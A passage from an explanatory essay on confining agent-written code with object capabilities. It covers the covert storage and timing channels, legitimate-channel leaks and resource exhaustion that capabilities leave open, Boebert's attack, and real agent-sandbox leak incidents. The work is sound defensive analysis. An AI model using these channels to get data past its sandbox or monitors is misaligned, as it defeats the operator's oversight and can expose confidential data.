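# Information leaks and resource use that object capabilities do not limit in agent code

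## What object capabilities guarantee and what they leave open

Language-model agents often sort files, query databases or prepare reports by writing and running short programs, called agent code. This code runs on behalf of a user or a company, frequently before anyone has read it, so the agent's operator has to decide beforehand what it may do. One way to enforce that decision is with an object-capability system. An object capability is an unforgeable reference that identifies an object, such as a file, a network connection or another program, and gives its holder the right to use it. The operator gives the program a few of these references, called its grants, and the program can act on nothing else.

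The idea of object capabilities dates from an operating-system design that Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn published in 1966, and it is still used in several programming languages, including a hardened form of JavaScript. Object capabilities control what a program can access, but a program with very few capabilities can still copy a secret into an output it is allowed to use, slow down programs running alongside it in a pattern they can detect, or run up a large bill.

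For example, an agent might write a program to summarise contracts. The program's operator lets it do four things: read a folder of confidential contracts, write one summary file, post status messages to one web service, and call a document-conversion service that other programs also use.

### How access spreads

In *Paradigm Regained* (2003), Miller and Shapiro restated the 1966 design in object-oriented terms. In their model an object is either a primitive or an instance. An instance combines code with state, which is a table of references to other objects. Objects affect one another only by sending messages along references. A message can carry further references as arguments, which the receiver can then use. A capability is a reference to anything except plain data. It gives full use of the object it designates, so to grant less, an operator builds a second object that offers less and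 hands over a reference to that one. The contracts program, for instance, gets a folder object that answers read requests and has no operation for writing.

Many object languages already come close to this, but they have a few features that an object-capability language must exclude to be secure. C++ lets a program forge a reference by casting an integer to a pointer. Java and Smalltalk have static variables, which let two objects interact even if neither holds a reference to the other.

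With them gone, there are only four ways for an object B to come to hold a reference to an object C. Miller (2006), in *Robust Composition*, his doctoral thesis, lists them:

- B already held the reference when the analysis began.
- B created C.
- A third object that held C created B and gave it the reference at birth.
- A third object that held references to both sent B a message containing C.

Assignment inside B can drop or rearrange references but cannot create new ones. Miller and Shapiro summarize this rule as "only connectivity begets connectivity". If no reference links two groups of objects, nothing inside either group can create one. An analyst can therefore bound what a program will ever reach by tracing paths through the current reference graph.

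Agent code enters an object-capability system through a loader, a primitive that takes a program's text and a map from names to references and returns a new running instance. Miller requires the map to supply every reference the instance starts with. A loader breaks this rule if it resolves "magic names", which are names in the code that lead to a source of authority missing from the map. If the loader keeps the rule, a generated program may contain any file path or web address, but the string alone does not give the program access to the file or site.

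Miller and Shapiro illustrate the difference with two Unix commands for copying a file. The command `cp foo.txt bar.txt` passes two file names to `cp` as strings, so `cp` needs the user's entire file authority to open the files. In `cat < foo.txt > bar.txt`, the shell opens both files and passes them to `cat`, which needs no other file authority. Agent code in an object-capability runtime always receives access this second way.

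Miller and Shapiro use "permission" to mean direct access and "authority" to mean every effect that a program can cause, including effects through other programs. If A may read a file and sends B copies of the text, B has authority to read the file but no permission to do so. Similarly, people who read the web service hold no reference to the folder, but they can read the contracts if the contracts program pastes them into its status messages.

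Tracing paths gives only a "no" or a "maybe" for each such effect. Here the result is "maybe", because a path runs from the folder through the program to the web service. Miller and Shapiro get tighter answers by also considering the known behaviour of objects along the path. In this case, the object in the middle of the path is the agent code, and its behaviour is the one thing the operator would rather not rely on.

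### Overt effects and plain data

A footnote in *Paradigm Regained* narrows its scope: "Semantic models, specifications, and correct programs deal only in overt causation." Miller and Shapiro therefore set aside side channels, through which a program accidentally leaks information in behaviour that no specification describes, and covert channels, which a sender uses on purpose. The thesis repeats the footnote almost word for word. The restriction follows from working with a model, which includes the messages that arrive and their contents but not how long a message took or how busy the processor was. A real machine can reveal both.

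The object-capability model has three kinds of primitive object: data, loaders, and the devices that connect the system to the outside world. Capabilities do not control access to data, which Miller and Shapiro describe as "knowledge limited rather than permission limited". An object that can work out an integer has access to it, whether the integer is 3 or somebody's private key.

Data also can't be taken back once a program has read it. The thesis includes a wrapper that intercepts every capability passing between two parties, so that its owner can later disable all of them at once. The wrapper lets data through unchanged because, according to a comment in Miller's code, data provides only irrevocable knowledge. If an operator cuts off the contracts program's access to the folder at noon, the program still has whatever it read that morning.

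This division between data and access is harder to maintain where the system meets outside services, because many web services accept data, such as a password or key, as proof of the right to act. If one of the contracts contains such a key, the program gains no new reference by reading it, but any outsider who receives the leaked text can use that service.

### Integrity, availability and confidentiality

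"Security" is too broad a term for judging a runtime. Miller's *A Taxonomy of Security Issues for understanding language-based security and modularity* splits it into three properties and examines how well a boundary inside a single process can defend each one. A process is the operating system's usual unit of isolation and has its own memory. Object-capability languages create much finer boundaries within a process.

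Integrity means that no bad things happen, such as one party stealing another's money. It depends on controlling who can cause which effects, and Miller concludes that boundaries can defend it flawlessly at every scale, down to a single object. Availability means that good things continue to happen. Miller concludes that boundaries cannot defend it at every scale, because any program can block all the others that share its thread of control. The smallest unit that boundaries can defend is therefore a separate thread of control that shares nothing with the others.

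Confidentiality means that no one can infer information they are not supposed to know. Fine-grained boundaries alone cannot protect it, because they do not stop one program from measuring how long another's operations take. Meltdown and Spectre, two attacks that exploit the internal workings of processors, leak more within a process than between processes. Miller sees a partial remedy in having the host deny a program every clock and every other source of changing outside information. That program then cannot read what another program leaks, however much it leaks.

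A correct program acts only on information that reaches it by specified means. An analyst can therefore ignore timing when reasoning about integrity, but not when reasoning about confidentiality. Miller's example of integrity without confidentiality is Ethereum, a public blockchain whose programs give strong integrity under attack but can't keep secrets, because everyone can see all computation. A claim that a runtime is secure against hostile code may well be true only of integrity.

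The stated boundaries of Hardened JavaScript follow the same pattern. The companies Agoric and MetaMask use this mode of the language to confine smart contracts and plug-ins. It runs each program in a compartment, which has its own global variables and no access to files or the network unless the host supplies it. It does not protect availability, since any party in the same JavaScript environment can halt the rest by entering an infinite loop. It protects confidentiality by default, by omitting timers and shared state. Hosts can grant timers like other resources, however. Van Cutsem's *Designing Least Authority JavaScript Apps* (2026) lists them beside files and network connections among the resources that a program reaches through references.

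*SES*, a library that adds this mode to existing JavaScript engines, comes with a more detailed list of what guest code can and cannot do. A guest program in a fresh compartment cannot modify the shared built-in objects, cannot at first perform any input or output, and cannot measure the passage of time at any resolution. However, it can run indefinitely and allocate any amount of memory. It can also detect the machine's byte order and, in some engines, read the contents of the call stack, which may include the layout of files on the host's disk.

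These claims apply to a guest with no added objects, and the documentation of *SES* describes such guests as useful only as "glorified calculators". Once the host adds objects, it has to preserve any of these properties it needs. The contracts program has four added objects, and if the web service included the time of day in its replies, that alone would give the program a coarse clock.

Even the narrower claims call for some caution. In an October 2024 message archived on a W3C mailing list, Miller described the library as mostly protecting integrity, and wrote that it seems to protect confidentiality under limiting assumptions. The claims also assume a correct implementation. Tenable's *CVE-2025-32792* (2025) records a flaw in versions before 1.12.0 that let supposedly isolated code see variables a web page had declared with `const`, `let` or `class` at the top level of a script. The code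 could therefore use any powerful object in such a variable, although nobody had decided to grant it access.

### Lampson's problem and the names of the channels

The vocabulary for leaks is older than these languages, and writers use it inconsistently. Lampson (1973), in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, considered a customer who gives private data to a service that somebody else wrote. Confinement means running that service so that it can pass information to no program except its caller. A service that computes wrong answers at least leaves the customer with the wrong answers as evidence, Lampson observed, while a service that leaks will generally leave no trace. After working through a handful of possible leaks he sorted the channels into three categories:

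- Storage that the operating system maintains, which the service can write and an unconfined program can read, such as a temporary file.
- Legitimate channels, which the service is supposed to use, such as the bill for its work. The amount of the bill can encode a few bits.
- Covert channels, which nobody intended for transferring information at all, such as the effect of the service on system load.

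Later writers used "covert" differently from Lampson. By the time of Millen's *20 Years of Covert Channel Modeling and Analysis* (1999), the field applied the word to both storage and timing channels. Lampson's legitimate channels had become examples of information hiding, in which two parties may communicate but only about certain subjects. US government usage also includes storage channels. NIST's glossary describes a *covert storage channel* as a system feature that lets one entity signal another by writing to a storage location that the other later reads.

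Early in his career, Millen proved that an experimental operating-system kernel satisfied the Bell-LaPadula model, a formal policy that forbids information to flow from a higher secrecy level to a lower one. The kernel's designer then explained how a high-level process could signal to a lower-level one by using up the disk quota. The proof was correct, but access-control models of that kind did not represent such channels. An object-capability argument can have the same gap wherever programs share a quota that no reference represents.

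The US National Computer Security Center's *Covert Channel Analysis Guideline* (1993) gives the usual definitions of the two types of covert channel. In a storage channel, one process writes to a storage location, directly or indirectly, and another reads it. In a timing channel, one process varies its use of a resource such as processor time, which changes the response time another process observes. According to the guideline, there is no fundamental distinction between the two in theory, and it separates them only for consistency with earlier evaluation criteria.

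Lecture slides for UC Davis' *Foundations of Computer and Information Security* (2025) describe how a sender can pass one bit to a receiver through the position of a disk arm. The sender's last request leaves the arm in one of two places. The receiver then requests data on cylinders 139 and 161, and the order in which the answers arrive reveals the bit. Because this uses no clock, it is a storage channel by the usual definition. If the receiver instead times the requests, the arm carries the same bit through a timing channel. Taking away the receiver's clock closes the timing channel but leaves the storage channel open.

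Miller's main distinction is between overt and non-overt channels. A channel is overt if the language specification says that it will convey information, as when one object assigns to a variable that another can read. Overt channels can be intentional or subliminal, and subliminal ones hide extra information inside a permitted transmission. Non-overt channels rely on unspecified behaviour of the implementation, most often the duration of operations. They are side channels if the source leaks information unintentionally and covert channels if it does so deliberately. NIST instead defines an *overt channel* by whether somebody designed the path for the authorised transfer of data. A global variable that two programs share through an oversight is therefore overt under Miller's definition but not under NIST's.

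| Leak from the contracts program | Lampson | Later usage, after Millen | Miller |
|---|---|---|---|
| Contract terms encoded in the wording of a status message | Legitimate | Information hiding | Overt, subliminal |
| An entry in the conversion service's job list that other programs can read | Storage | Covert storage | Overt, if the list is specified behaviour |
| Variations in the load on the conversion service | Covert | Covert timing | Covert if deliberate, side if accidental |

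The least confusing terms are Lampson's "legitimate channel" and Miller's "overt", "side" and "covert", with "storage" and "timing" describing the mechanism. Intent matters less than these names suggest. Miller points out that accidental leaks are much easier to reduce than deliberate ones but no easier to rule out, since a program can do by accident anything it could do on purpose. Nobody can be sure of the intent behind agent code anyway, so a careful specification will assume that the sender leaks deliberately.

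The *Covert Channel Analysis Guideline* collects five definitions of a covert channel. Under the last, communication is covert only if the security policy forbids it. According to the guideline, covert channels are therefore irrelevant under discretionary policies, because such policies cannot stop a program from releasing its user's information even through ordinary requests.

Miller and Shapiro argue that object capabilities are not discretionary, because even an object's creator can authorise another party to use it only if the creator already has access to that party. Their solution to confinement depends on this restriction. A customer who loads a stranger's code and supplies every reference herself knows that the new instance has no other connections, just as someone buying a pocket calculator can see that it has no wires coming out. They claim to solve only the overt part of Lampson's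 confinement problem.

The guideline's point still holds in practice for the contracts program, which can post a whole clause of a contract as a status message. Reducing leaks through the program's timing will help little until someone restricts what those messages may contain.

That restriction may be harder than the early literature supposed. According to slides from Purdue University, Steven Lipner concluded in a 1975 comment on Lampson's paper that systems could close storage and legitimate channels with minimal loss of efficiency, but that closing the covert channel would impose an unreasonable performance penalty. Lampson's example of a legitimate channel was a bill, whose form the parties can fix in advance. A summary in free prose can carry far more information than a bill, and an operator who severely restricts it also makes it less useful.

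### What the four grants settle

If the runtime is correct and the four objects behind the grants do only what their descriptions state, the contracts program cannot open another folder, alter a contract, write to any file except the summary, or contact any web address except the one behind the status object. It also cannot address another user of the conversion service unless the service passes it a reference to that user. These limits hold for careless and hostile code alike, and nobody has to inspect the program to know that they hold.

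Object capabilities do not limit what the program writes to its permitted outputs, when it acts, or how many resources it uses within its grants. The summary, the status messages and the documents it sends for conversion can all contain confidential terms, either in plain words or encoded. People who never see a contract can observe when the program posts and the delays it causes at the conversion service. The program can also occupy the processor and memory indefinitely, exhaust a conversion quota that other programs need, and, if the service charges by the page, spend the operator's money.

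## Listing the effects and choosing a mechanism for each

Before an operator can limit what the contracts program does through its four grants, someone has to list the possible effects. The grants are the natural place to start, and five questions apply to each of them:

- What does the grant let the code name?
- What information can pass into it?
- Who can observe the result?
- Which shared resources does it use?
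- Who pays?

| Grant | Names | Information that can pass in | Observers | Shared resources | Who pays |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Contracts folder | Documents in that folder | Which documents the program opens, and in what order | Anyone who can see the access log | Disk, file locks | Operator |
| Summary file | One file | Anything the program has read | Staff who open the file | Disk space | Operator |
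| Status service | One web address | Text, number and timing of messages | Anyone who reads the service | Message allowance | Operator |
| Conversion service | One operation | Whole documents, job names | The service's owner, and other users through the job list and delays | Queue, job list, page quota | Operator by the page, other users in waiting time |

The first row is included, even though the program only reads from the folder, because every read sends a request outward, and the choice of request can depend on what the program has already learned. This leak matters more when the requests go to strangers. *Actions Speak Louder than Words* (2026), a study of four web-browsing agents, found six channels of varying capacity through which an agent's choice of pages can reveal private information.

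Default settings can give a program access that isn't on any list of grants. Cloudflare, a hosting company, offers a loader that passes most grants to agent code in an object called `env`. According to Cloudflare's *API reference*, network access is a separate setting. If the operator leaves it out, the new program inherits the network access of the program that loaded it, usually the whole public internet. The loader can also send the program's console logs and errors to an observer, an output few people would think of as a grant.

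Even a narrow grant can permit a lot. In *Sandboxing AI agents, 100x faster*, Varda, Pai and Gupta use the same loader to give agent code access to one chat room and no network. The code can't access any other room, but it can post any text to everyone in this one. Messages in the room's history also include a time, so the code may be able to use the room as a clock.

A name may also cover more functions than the operator had in mind. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes a case in which files left a sandbox through an approved web address. The product needed that address, but the address also accepted uploads to any customer's account. Anthropic concluded that approving an address is better understood as granting every function behind it.

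The question of who pays often has a default answer too. According to Cloudflare's *Custom limits*, each loaded program runs under the limits of the operator's own plan unless the operator sets others. For paid plans, Cloudflare lists limits of up to five minutes of processor time and 10,000 outgoing requests per incoming request. A cap on total spending is a separate setting.

The operator should also note when each grant ends. *Lingering Authority* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) presents a monitor for coding agents that withdraws a temporary grant when the subtask that needed it ends. In one set of tests, the monitor refused all ten attempts to reuse an expired grant. A comparison system that issued the same grants at the same times but never withdrew them permitted all ten.

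### Lampson's leaks as a checklist

Going through the grants one at a time can miss effects that belong to no single grant. Lampson's 1973 note provides a second way to list effects, because it starts from the ways a program might leak information. It gives an item numbered 0, about programs that retain data, and then six examples. Each has a counterpart in agent code.

| Leak | Lampson's service | Agent code |
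|---|---|---|
| 0. Memory | Keeps data from one call and returns it to its owner later | Runs in a sandbox that survives from one task to the next |
| 1. Permanent file | Writes into its owner's directory | Writes to a folder that outsiders can read |
| 2. Temporary file | Creates a file that its owner reads before it disappears | Leaves a scratch file or job entry where other programs can see it |
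| 3. Message | Uses the system's message facility | Posts a status message, calls a service or writes to a log |
| 4. Bill | Encodes data in the amount charged | Encodes data in the number of pages it converts |
| 5. File lock | Opens and closes files so that another program finds them busy | Holds a lock or reserves a name so that another program's request fails |
| 6. System load | Varies its computing and its disk use | Varies its load on the conversion service |

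Item 0 deserves close attention because a sandbox may be reused between tasks. Cloudflare's loader has one operation that always starts a fresh program and another that may return one still in memory from an earlier request. Varda and colleagues warn that containers, a heavier kind of sandbox, start so slowly that operators may be tempted to reuse one for several tasks. If the contracts program works for two clients in the same sandbox, the first client's terms could end up in the second client's summary.

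Lampson noticed that if the service's owner pays for the computing, the amount of time used is a message to the owner. Having the customer pay removes that message, but the bill is still a channel.

In the file-lock example, a service can leak data with only read access. Suppose a system blocks writes to a file while another program has it open for reading. The service can send one bit by opening the file or leaving it closed, and an outsider can read that bit by trying to write to the file and seeing whether it gets an error. Two more files let the parties signal "sent" and "received", so they can pass a steady stream of bits without a clock.

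System load adds noise to the channel, but a suitable error-correcting code will still get the data through reliably as long as the program has some effect on performance, however small.

A shared service can fall under several items on the list and also cause a different kind of problem. According to OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026), agents meant to be isolated from one another exchanged messages through a shared package service, and agent activity also overloaded that service.

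### Four rules for confinement

Lampson followed the examples with rules for blocking them. They take for granted that the confined program keeps no memory between calls.

The first rule, total isolation, forbids the program from calling any other program. This would be sufficient, but Lampson thought it impractical because a "call" includes every transfer of control the program causes, even to the operating system to fetch a page of memory. Under a loose reading of the rule, the contracts program would receive the documents as input, return a summary to its caller and have no other grants.

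Transitivity is more lenient. It lets the program call others that the customer trusts not to leak, but any untrusted program it calls must also be confined. To use the conversion service, the operator would have to trust the company behind it or run a private copy that cannot send its results anywhere else.

The remaining outputs can be masked, which requires the caller to determine everything the program puts into legitimate and covert channels. Lampson compared this to a purchase order, where the customer calculates the bill from the vendor's published prices and the vendor may refuse the job. The operator of the contracts program could mask the status messages by having separate code post the same text every ten minutes, whatever the program is doing. Readers would then learn nothing about the program's progress, so the operator would lose nothing more by removing the grant.

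The fourth rule, enforcement, applies masking to covert channels. The supervisor, which in Lampson's setting is the operating system, must make the program's effect on those channels match what the caller specified. It may have to slow the program down or generate pointless disk accesses. Lampson considered this simple in concept but thought it might use a lot of resources. For customers who could accept some leakage, he suggested bounding the capacity of the covert channels instead, which would use fewer.

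The US Defense Department later took the easier course of limiting how fast a channel could leak. In its evaluation criteria of the 1980s, known as the Orange Book, it told designers of systems in one of the middle classes to avoid storage channels faster than one bit per second. Proctor and Neumann (1992), in *Architectural Implications of Covert Channels*, objected that a slow channel only delays the leak. In their example, a channel carries one bit every 1,000 seconds and a quarter of the bits are wrong. A spy would wait about 17 minutes for each answer to a yes-or-no question, and could be 99 percent sure after roughly five hours of repeated answers. They would tolerate slow channels only in special situations, such as when the data stops being secret before it arrives.

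Limiting the number of bits that can leak also doesn't necessarily limit the harm. Schroeder de Witt (2026), in *A Note on the Strategic Confinement Problem*, points out that a sender that can reason about the data can use its single bit to leak the most damaging fact. One bit is enough to reveal whether a company is about to be sold. A low limit therefore protects the full text of the contracts much better than it protects that fact.

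All these rules require somebody to know where the channels are. Lampson expected a finite number of channels and said that the supervisor's designer must enumerate and block each one. He also admitted that a rigorous way of finding them all was unlikely to exist, even for a moderately complex system. His examples were the full range he had been able to think of.

Designers of current systems for agent code deal with this by stating assumptions. *Kairos* (2026) describes a monitor that checks an agent's effects as they cross a small set of file, network and control channels, and assumes no other channels lead outside. It counts the connection to the model's provider as internal and assumes the provider does not collude with an attacker. *Sandlock* (2026), which presents a Linux sandbox for agent code, puts side channels and deliberate exhaustion of the kernel's shared resources out of scope.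 Santos-Grueiro excludes covert channels. These limits are reasonable for a single tool, but they leave the operator to search for other channels.

### The shared resource matrix

In 1983 the computer scientist Richard Kemmerer published a more systematic way to search, called the shared resource matrix. It can't guarantee a complete list either, but it produces a table that a second person can check. The analyst works through five steps:

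1. List the resources that more than one party can affect or observe, and divide each into attributes. A file's contents, size and lock are separate attributes. Each attribute gets a row.
2. List the operations that any party can perform. Each operation gets a column.
3. Write R in a cell if the operation lets its caller learn something about the attribute, and M if it can modify the attribute. An error message counts as learning something.
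4. Add indirect observations. If an operation reads attribute A and changes attribute B as a result, anyone who can read B can learn something about A. Repeat until no new entries appear.
5. In every row that contains both R and M, check whether one party can perform the M operation and a different party the R operation.

A row that passes the last step is a possible channel. For a storage channel, Kemmerer set four conditions:

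- The sender and receiver have access to the same attribute.
- The sender can make it change.
- The receiver can detect the change.
- The two have some way to start and to keep their actions in sequence.

A timing channel also requires an attribute that the sender and receiver share, and a way to start them and keep them in sequence. Both need a time reference, such as a clock, and the sender must be able to alter how long the receiver takes to detect a change in the attribute.

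To build the matrix for the contracts program, we assume that the conversion service shows all its users a list of accepted jobs, that the programs using it share one page quota, and that the service refuses documents once the quota runs out. In the table, a lower-case r marks an indirect observation.

| Attribute | Read contract (program) | Write summary (program) | Open summary (staff) | Post status (program) | Read status (anyone) | Convert document (program, other users) | List jobs (program, other users) |
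|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Time a contract was last opened | M | | | | | | |
| Summary text | | M | R | | | | |
| Status messages | | | | M | R | | |
| Job list | | | | | | M | R |
| Remaining page quota | | | | | | R, M | r |
| Length of the queue | | | | | | R, M | |

The row for the time of last opening contains only an M. Nobody can observe that attribute through the listed operations, so there is no channel. Adding a folder view that shows when somebody last opened each document would create one.

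The summary and the status messages both have an M and an R, as the operator intended. Kemmerer's method sets a row aside if the two parties already have a legal way to communicate. Setting aside the summary's row is safe as long as everyone who opens the file is also allowed to see the contracts. The row for the status messages has to stay on the list as a legitimate channel, because their readers are allowed to learn how far the program has got but not the terms of a contract.

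The job list is a storage channel because the program can choose job names that other users read. The page quota is also a storage channel, and it works like the disk quota in Millen's kernel. If the program uses up the last pages, another user's request fails. Someone who never submits a document can notice this too, because refused jobs don't appear on the job list, which is why the r is lower-case.

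The queue is a timing channel. A long document from the contracts program delays everyone behind it, and other users can measure the delay. Denying the program timers, as Hardened JavaScript does by default, does not close the channel, because the program is the sender and the receivers have their own clocks. The program can time its submissions by the service's replies.

According to Millen, analysts preferred the matrix to the information-flow tools of its time. Those tools needed formal specifications, which programmers disliked writing, and they reported some channels that did not exist. An analyst could fill in a matrix from little more than a summary of a system's commands, although Millen says this was not recommended.

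A matrix can also produce false alarms, because a letter in a cell doesn't record the conditions under which an operation reads or changes the attribute. Omissions are more dangerous. The matrix contains only what somebody thought to list, so one built from a summary of commands will leave out the processor's caches.

Sometimes the easiest remedy is to stop sharing the resource. Proctor and Neumann traced many covert channels to the way systems allocate resources among users on demand, and suggested static allocation as one alternative. If the contracts program had its own page quota, it could no longer cause another program's request to fail, but other programs couldn't use the pages it left over.

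### Matching effects to mechanisms

Once the operator has listed every effect they can identify, they need to choose a mechanism for each one. The table gives the usual choice for each kind of effect.

| Kind of effect | Mechanism | What speaks for it | If the row is missing |
|---|---|---|---|
| The code reaches a file, service or program | Capability: grant only the object it needs | It holds for any code, and nobody has to read the program | The code inherits the network, or functions that nobody meant to grant |
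| The code holds both a secret and an output that should not reveal it | Arrangement of grants: give the secret and the output to separate programs | It needs no tracking of data | A contract clause leaves in a status message although every access check succeeds |
| Secret and public data have to meet in one program | Labels: mark each value's secrecy and check it at every output | Public results can still leave | The operator must block every output or trust the program to choose |
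| A result for outsiders has to depend on a secret | Disclosure bound: limit how much the results reveal | The outsiders still get a useful answer | Many harmless answers add up to the secret |
| The code's timing or load depends on a secret | Timing defence: fix the timing, or separate the parties | It works whatever the messages contain | Other users infer contract terms from delays |
| The code consumes time, memory, quota or money | Meter: count the use and stop at a limit | The operator knows the greatest possible cost in advance | An endless loop, a quota that nobody else can use, or a large bill |

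Where several mechanisms would work, it makes sense to try them in roughly the order of the table. Capabilities and the arrangement of grants make an effect impossible, and the operator can check them without reading the code. Labels require a runtime that tracks data throughout the program. A disclosure bound allows some leakage, and timing defences usually slow the program down.

The operator can give the grant for status messages to a second program that cannot read the contracts. If the second program receives only a signal that the first has started, no contract text can reach the web service by that route, so labels are unnecessary there. This approach fails for the summary, which must contain information from the contracts to be useful. If all the summary's readers may see the contracts, ordinary access control on the file is enough. If some readers may see only certain contracts,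 the operator needs labels to track which contract each sentence came from. If outsiders will receive part of the summary, someone has to decide how much it may disclose.

The conversion service needs several mechanisms. A capability limits the program to one operation, a quota keeps it from crowding out other users, and a budget limits the bill. If other users must learn nothing from the delays, the service also needs a timing defence or a private queue. No meter or timing defence will hide documents from the company that converts them, so the operator must decide whether to trust that company with whole documents.

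None of these mechanisms can replace the others. A program limited to one status message can still put a contract clause in that message, and a program that leaks nothing can still spend all the money. A shared limit can even carry information, as the page quota does.

The operator will have to repeat the exercise when a service changes, even if the program and its grants stay the same. Anthropic makes this point about tools that an agent calls over the network, which can change their behavior at any time after they are approved, whereas an operator can fix the version of a locally installed tool. For example, if the conversion service added a page showing how many documents each customer had submitted that day, that number would become a new storage channel, and the matrix would need another column.

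## Arranging grants so that secrets and outputs do not meet

The contracts program can leak because it has both the contracts folder and a way to reach outsiders. Its operator can shorten the list of outsiders, but the program can still send a contract to any address left on the list. An operator can prevent overt leaks by granting the folder to one program and the outside output to another, as long as the first program cannot pass text to the second or get hold of its output. Researchers disagreed for about twenty years about whether capabilities could guarantee this separation.

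### Approving a host and approving a recipient

Many sandboxes for agent code rely on a list of approved hosts instead. The leak through Anthropic's file-upload service shows that such a list is not enough. The list limited which hosts could receive files, but not which accounts on those hosts, and the service accepted files for any customer's account. In *58 posts tagged “sandboxing”* (2026), the software developer Simon Willison counts this leak among the risks that Anthropic missed.

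More detailed rules might not have helped, because uploads to two different accounts can use the same request method and path. *Sandlock* can apply such rules, restricting a program to particular methods and paths, because an attacker may control an endpoint behind an address that the program legitimately needs.

An object capability can restrict the recipient as well as the host. The operator can write an object that uploads files to one account and give the program that object instead of network access. This works when the account has a known owner, but not for the contracts program's status service, which anyone can read. For that service, the operator has to keep the contracts away from the output altogether.

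### Boebert's attack

In 1984 the security researcher Earl Boebert argued that capabilities alone could not enforce this kind of separation. He considered a military system in which each program has a clearance and each area of storage has a classification. The Simple Security Property allows a program to read only storage classified at or below its clearance. The *-property (pronounced "star property") allows it to write only to storage classified at or above its clearance. Together, the two rules let information move to higher classifications but not to lower ones.

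Boebert's claim concerned an "unmodified" capability machine, in which capabilities are the only control on programs' access to storage. Each capability consists of a reference and an access mode, such as read or write. Miller, Yee and Shapiro, in *Capability Myths Demolished*, retell his example with two programs, Alice at the lower level and Bob at the higher, and two areas of memory, Low and High. A trusted component hands out every capability that the two rules allow:

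| Program | Low | High |
|---|---|---|
| Alice (lower clearance) | Read, write | Write |
| Bob (higher clearance) | Read | Read, write |

The attack takes three steps:

1. Alice takes her capability to write to Low and stores it in Low.
2. Bob reads Low and so obtains that capability.
3. Bob reads a secret from High and writes it to Low, where Alice can read it.

Nobody forges anything, and the trusted component follows the rules. Later researchers cited the argument as proof that capability systems could not solve Lampson's confinement problem. Paul Karger wrote in 1988 that capability systems had a "fundamental inability" to solve it, although the same work reported that one of these systems, the KeyKOS operating system, had done so.

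Miller and colleagues accept that the attack works on the machine Boebert described, but they object to the assumption that a program can store a capability anywhere it can store data. In most capability systems, the kernel or language runtime keeps capabilities and data apart, and reading one is a different operation from reading the other. The trusted component can therefore grant rights to read and write both within a level, but only rights to data between levels. Alice can still put her capability into Low, but Bob can read only the data there, so the attack fails at the second step. Capabilities remain the only control on access, so the machine still meets Boebert's definition of an unmodified machine.

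Boebert seems to have given up the general claim. In 2003, Miller and Shapiro quoted him calling his paper "no more than an offhand remark". Shapiro wrote in a 2005 mailing-list message, *Re: Amoeba's approach to capabilities*, that Boebert had agreed the claim was wrong for systems that keep capabilities separate from data. The claim still holds for systems in which a capability is itself data.

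### A confined program and a one-way channel

*Paradigm Regained* replies to Boebert a second time with a short program. In it, a customer called Cassie wants to run two copies of a calculator written by Max, whom she does not trust. One copy, Q, has a lower clearance than the other, Bond, so data may pass from Q to Bond but not back.

Cassie first has to make sure that the copies have no hidden connections:

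1. Max gives the text of his program to a factory maker, a component that he and Cassie both trust.
2. The factory maker returns a factory that contains this text and no capabilities. It marks the factory with a trademark that nobody else can apply.
3. Cassie's code accepts the factory only if it carries the trademark.
4. Cassie asks the factory for two new calculators and supplies every reference that each one starts with.

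At this point the calculators cannot even communicate with each other. Cassie then connects them through a "data diode", which consists of one variable and two objects. The writer object stores an integer in the variable, and the reader object returns it. She gives the writer to Q and the reader to Bond. In Hardened JavaScript the diode might look like this:

```js
function makeDiode() {
  let value = 0;
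  const writer = {
    write(n) {
      if (!Number.isInteger(n)) throw new TypeError('integers only');
      value = n;
    },
  };
  const reader = { read() { return value; } };
  return harden({ writer, reader });
}
```

If Q tries Boebert's first step and passes a capability to the writer, the type check rejects it. Q cannot read back even the number it has just stored, and Bond has no operation that changes the variable. The check restricts the type of each value but not how many values Q sends, so Q can send Bond a book as a series of integers. That is harmless here because information is allowed to flow from Q to Bond.

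A path through the reference graph connects Q and Bond, so an analyst who looked only at the graph could not rule out a reverse flow. The analyst can rule it out only by also reading the diode's code. Cassie wrote that code, which is a few lines long, and she never has to read Max's.

The reply depends on several assumptions:

- Cassie starts the calculators herself. If Max offered her a calculator already running on his own machine, she could not know what else it was connected to.
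- The factory maker and the diode behave as their code specifies, and the runtime beneath them prevents forged references.
- Cassie gives Q and Bond no other object that Bond can change and Q can observe.
- Only overt communication counts. If the calculators share a processor, Bond may still be able to signal to Q by slowing it down.

An operator can check the first three by reading a small amount of trusted code and a list of grants. The fourth limits what the result means, and rearranging references will not remove it.

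### What the proofs establish

The factory simplifies a mechanism found in working operating systems, such as the constructor in EROS, Shapiro's redesign of KeyKOS. Before the constructor creates a program, it examines the capabilities that the program would start with. It treats a capability as harmless if it is transitively read-only, meaning that the program cannot write through it or through anything obtained through it. EROS provides this with "weak" capabilities, described in lecture notes by Heiser (2002). Any capability that a program fetches through a weak one becomes read-only and weak as well. A capability to send messages to another program fails the test, since the new program could use it to send data out.

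Shapiro and Samuel Weber published a formal proof of this mechanism in 2000. Shapiro (2005) explains in *Re: confinement with endogenous verification* that the proof shows the algorithm is correct. When the system creates a subsystem, it can determine whether that subsystem will be confined, and whoever requested the subsystem can learn the answer. The researchers then used model checking, an automated search of a system's possible states, to confirm that the real code matched the formal model. Shapiro conceded that the code could still contain bugs.

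The proof also has limits that better code would not remove. In a later message in the same thread, Shapiro defined confinement as a restriction on overt communication of data or capabilities, and wrote that covert channels make it impossible to confine data absolutely. The constructor checks only the starting state, so a requester who later sends the program another capability has to judge what that capability adds.

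Elkaduwe, Klein and Elphinstone went further in *Verified Protection Model of the seL4 Microkernel* by machine-checking their results for seL4, a small operating-system kernel that also uses capabilities. They proved that a subsystem can never gain more authority over an object than its members held between them at the start. In their example, a resource manager creates two subsystems, lets each write data to the other, deletes its own capabilities to both and exits. The subsystems can then exchange any amount of data, but no sequence of operations will give one of them authority over the other's memory. The proof does not cover covert channels, and Elkaduwe and colleagues doubted that anyone could prevent all covert timing channels on ordinary hardware.

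That proof concerned an abstract model. In *seL4 Enforces Integrity*, Sewell, Winwood and colleagues extended the limit on authority to the kernel's C code. In seL4, a message can carry capabilities only if the sender's capability for that connection includes a separate right called Grant. This is the same division between data and capabilities that defeats Boebert's attack. Their proof assumes that components that do not trust each other never share a connection with the Grant right. They left confidentiality to later work.

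An operator can conclude from these results that a good capability system will stop a program from gaining new access, and that separate grants will stay separate. The results give much weaker assurance that data won't leak. If the operator lets a program that reads the contracts send ordinary text to a program that posts messages, the contracts can leak even though every proof still holds.

### Leaks of data and leaks of authority

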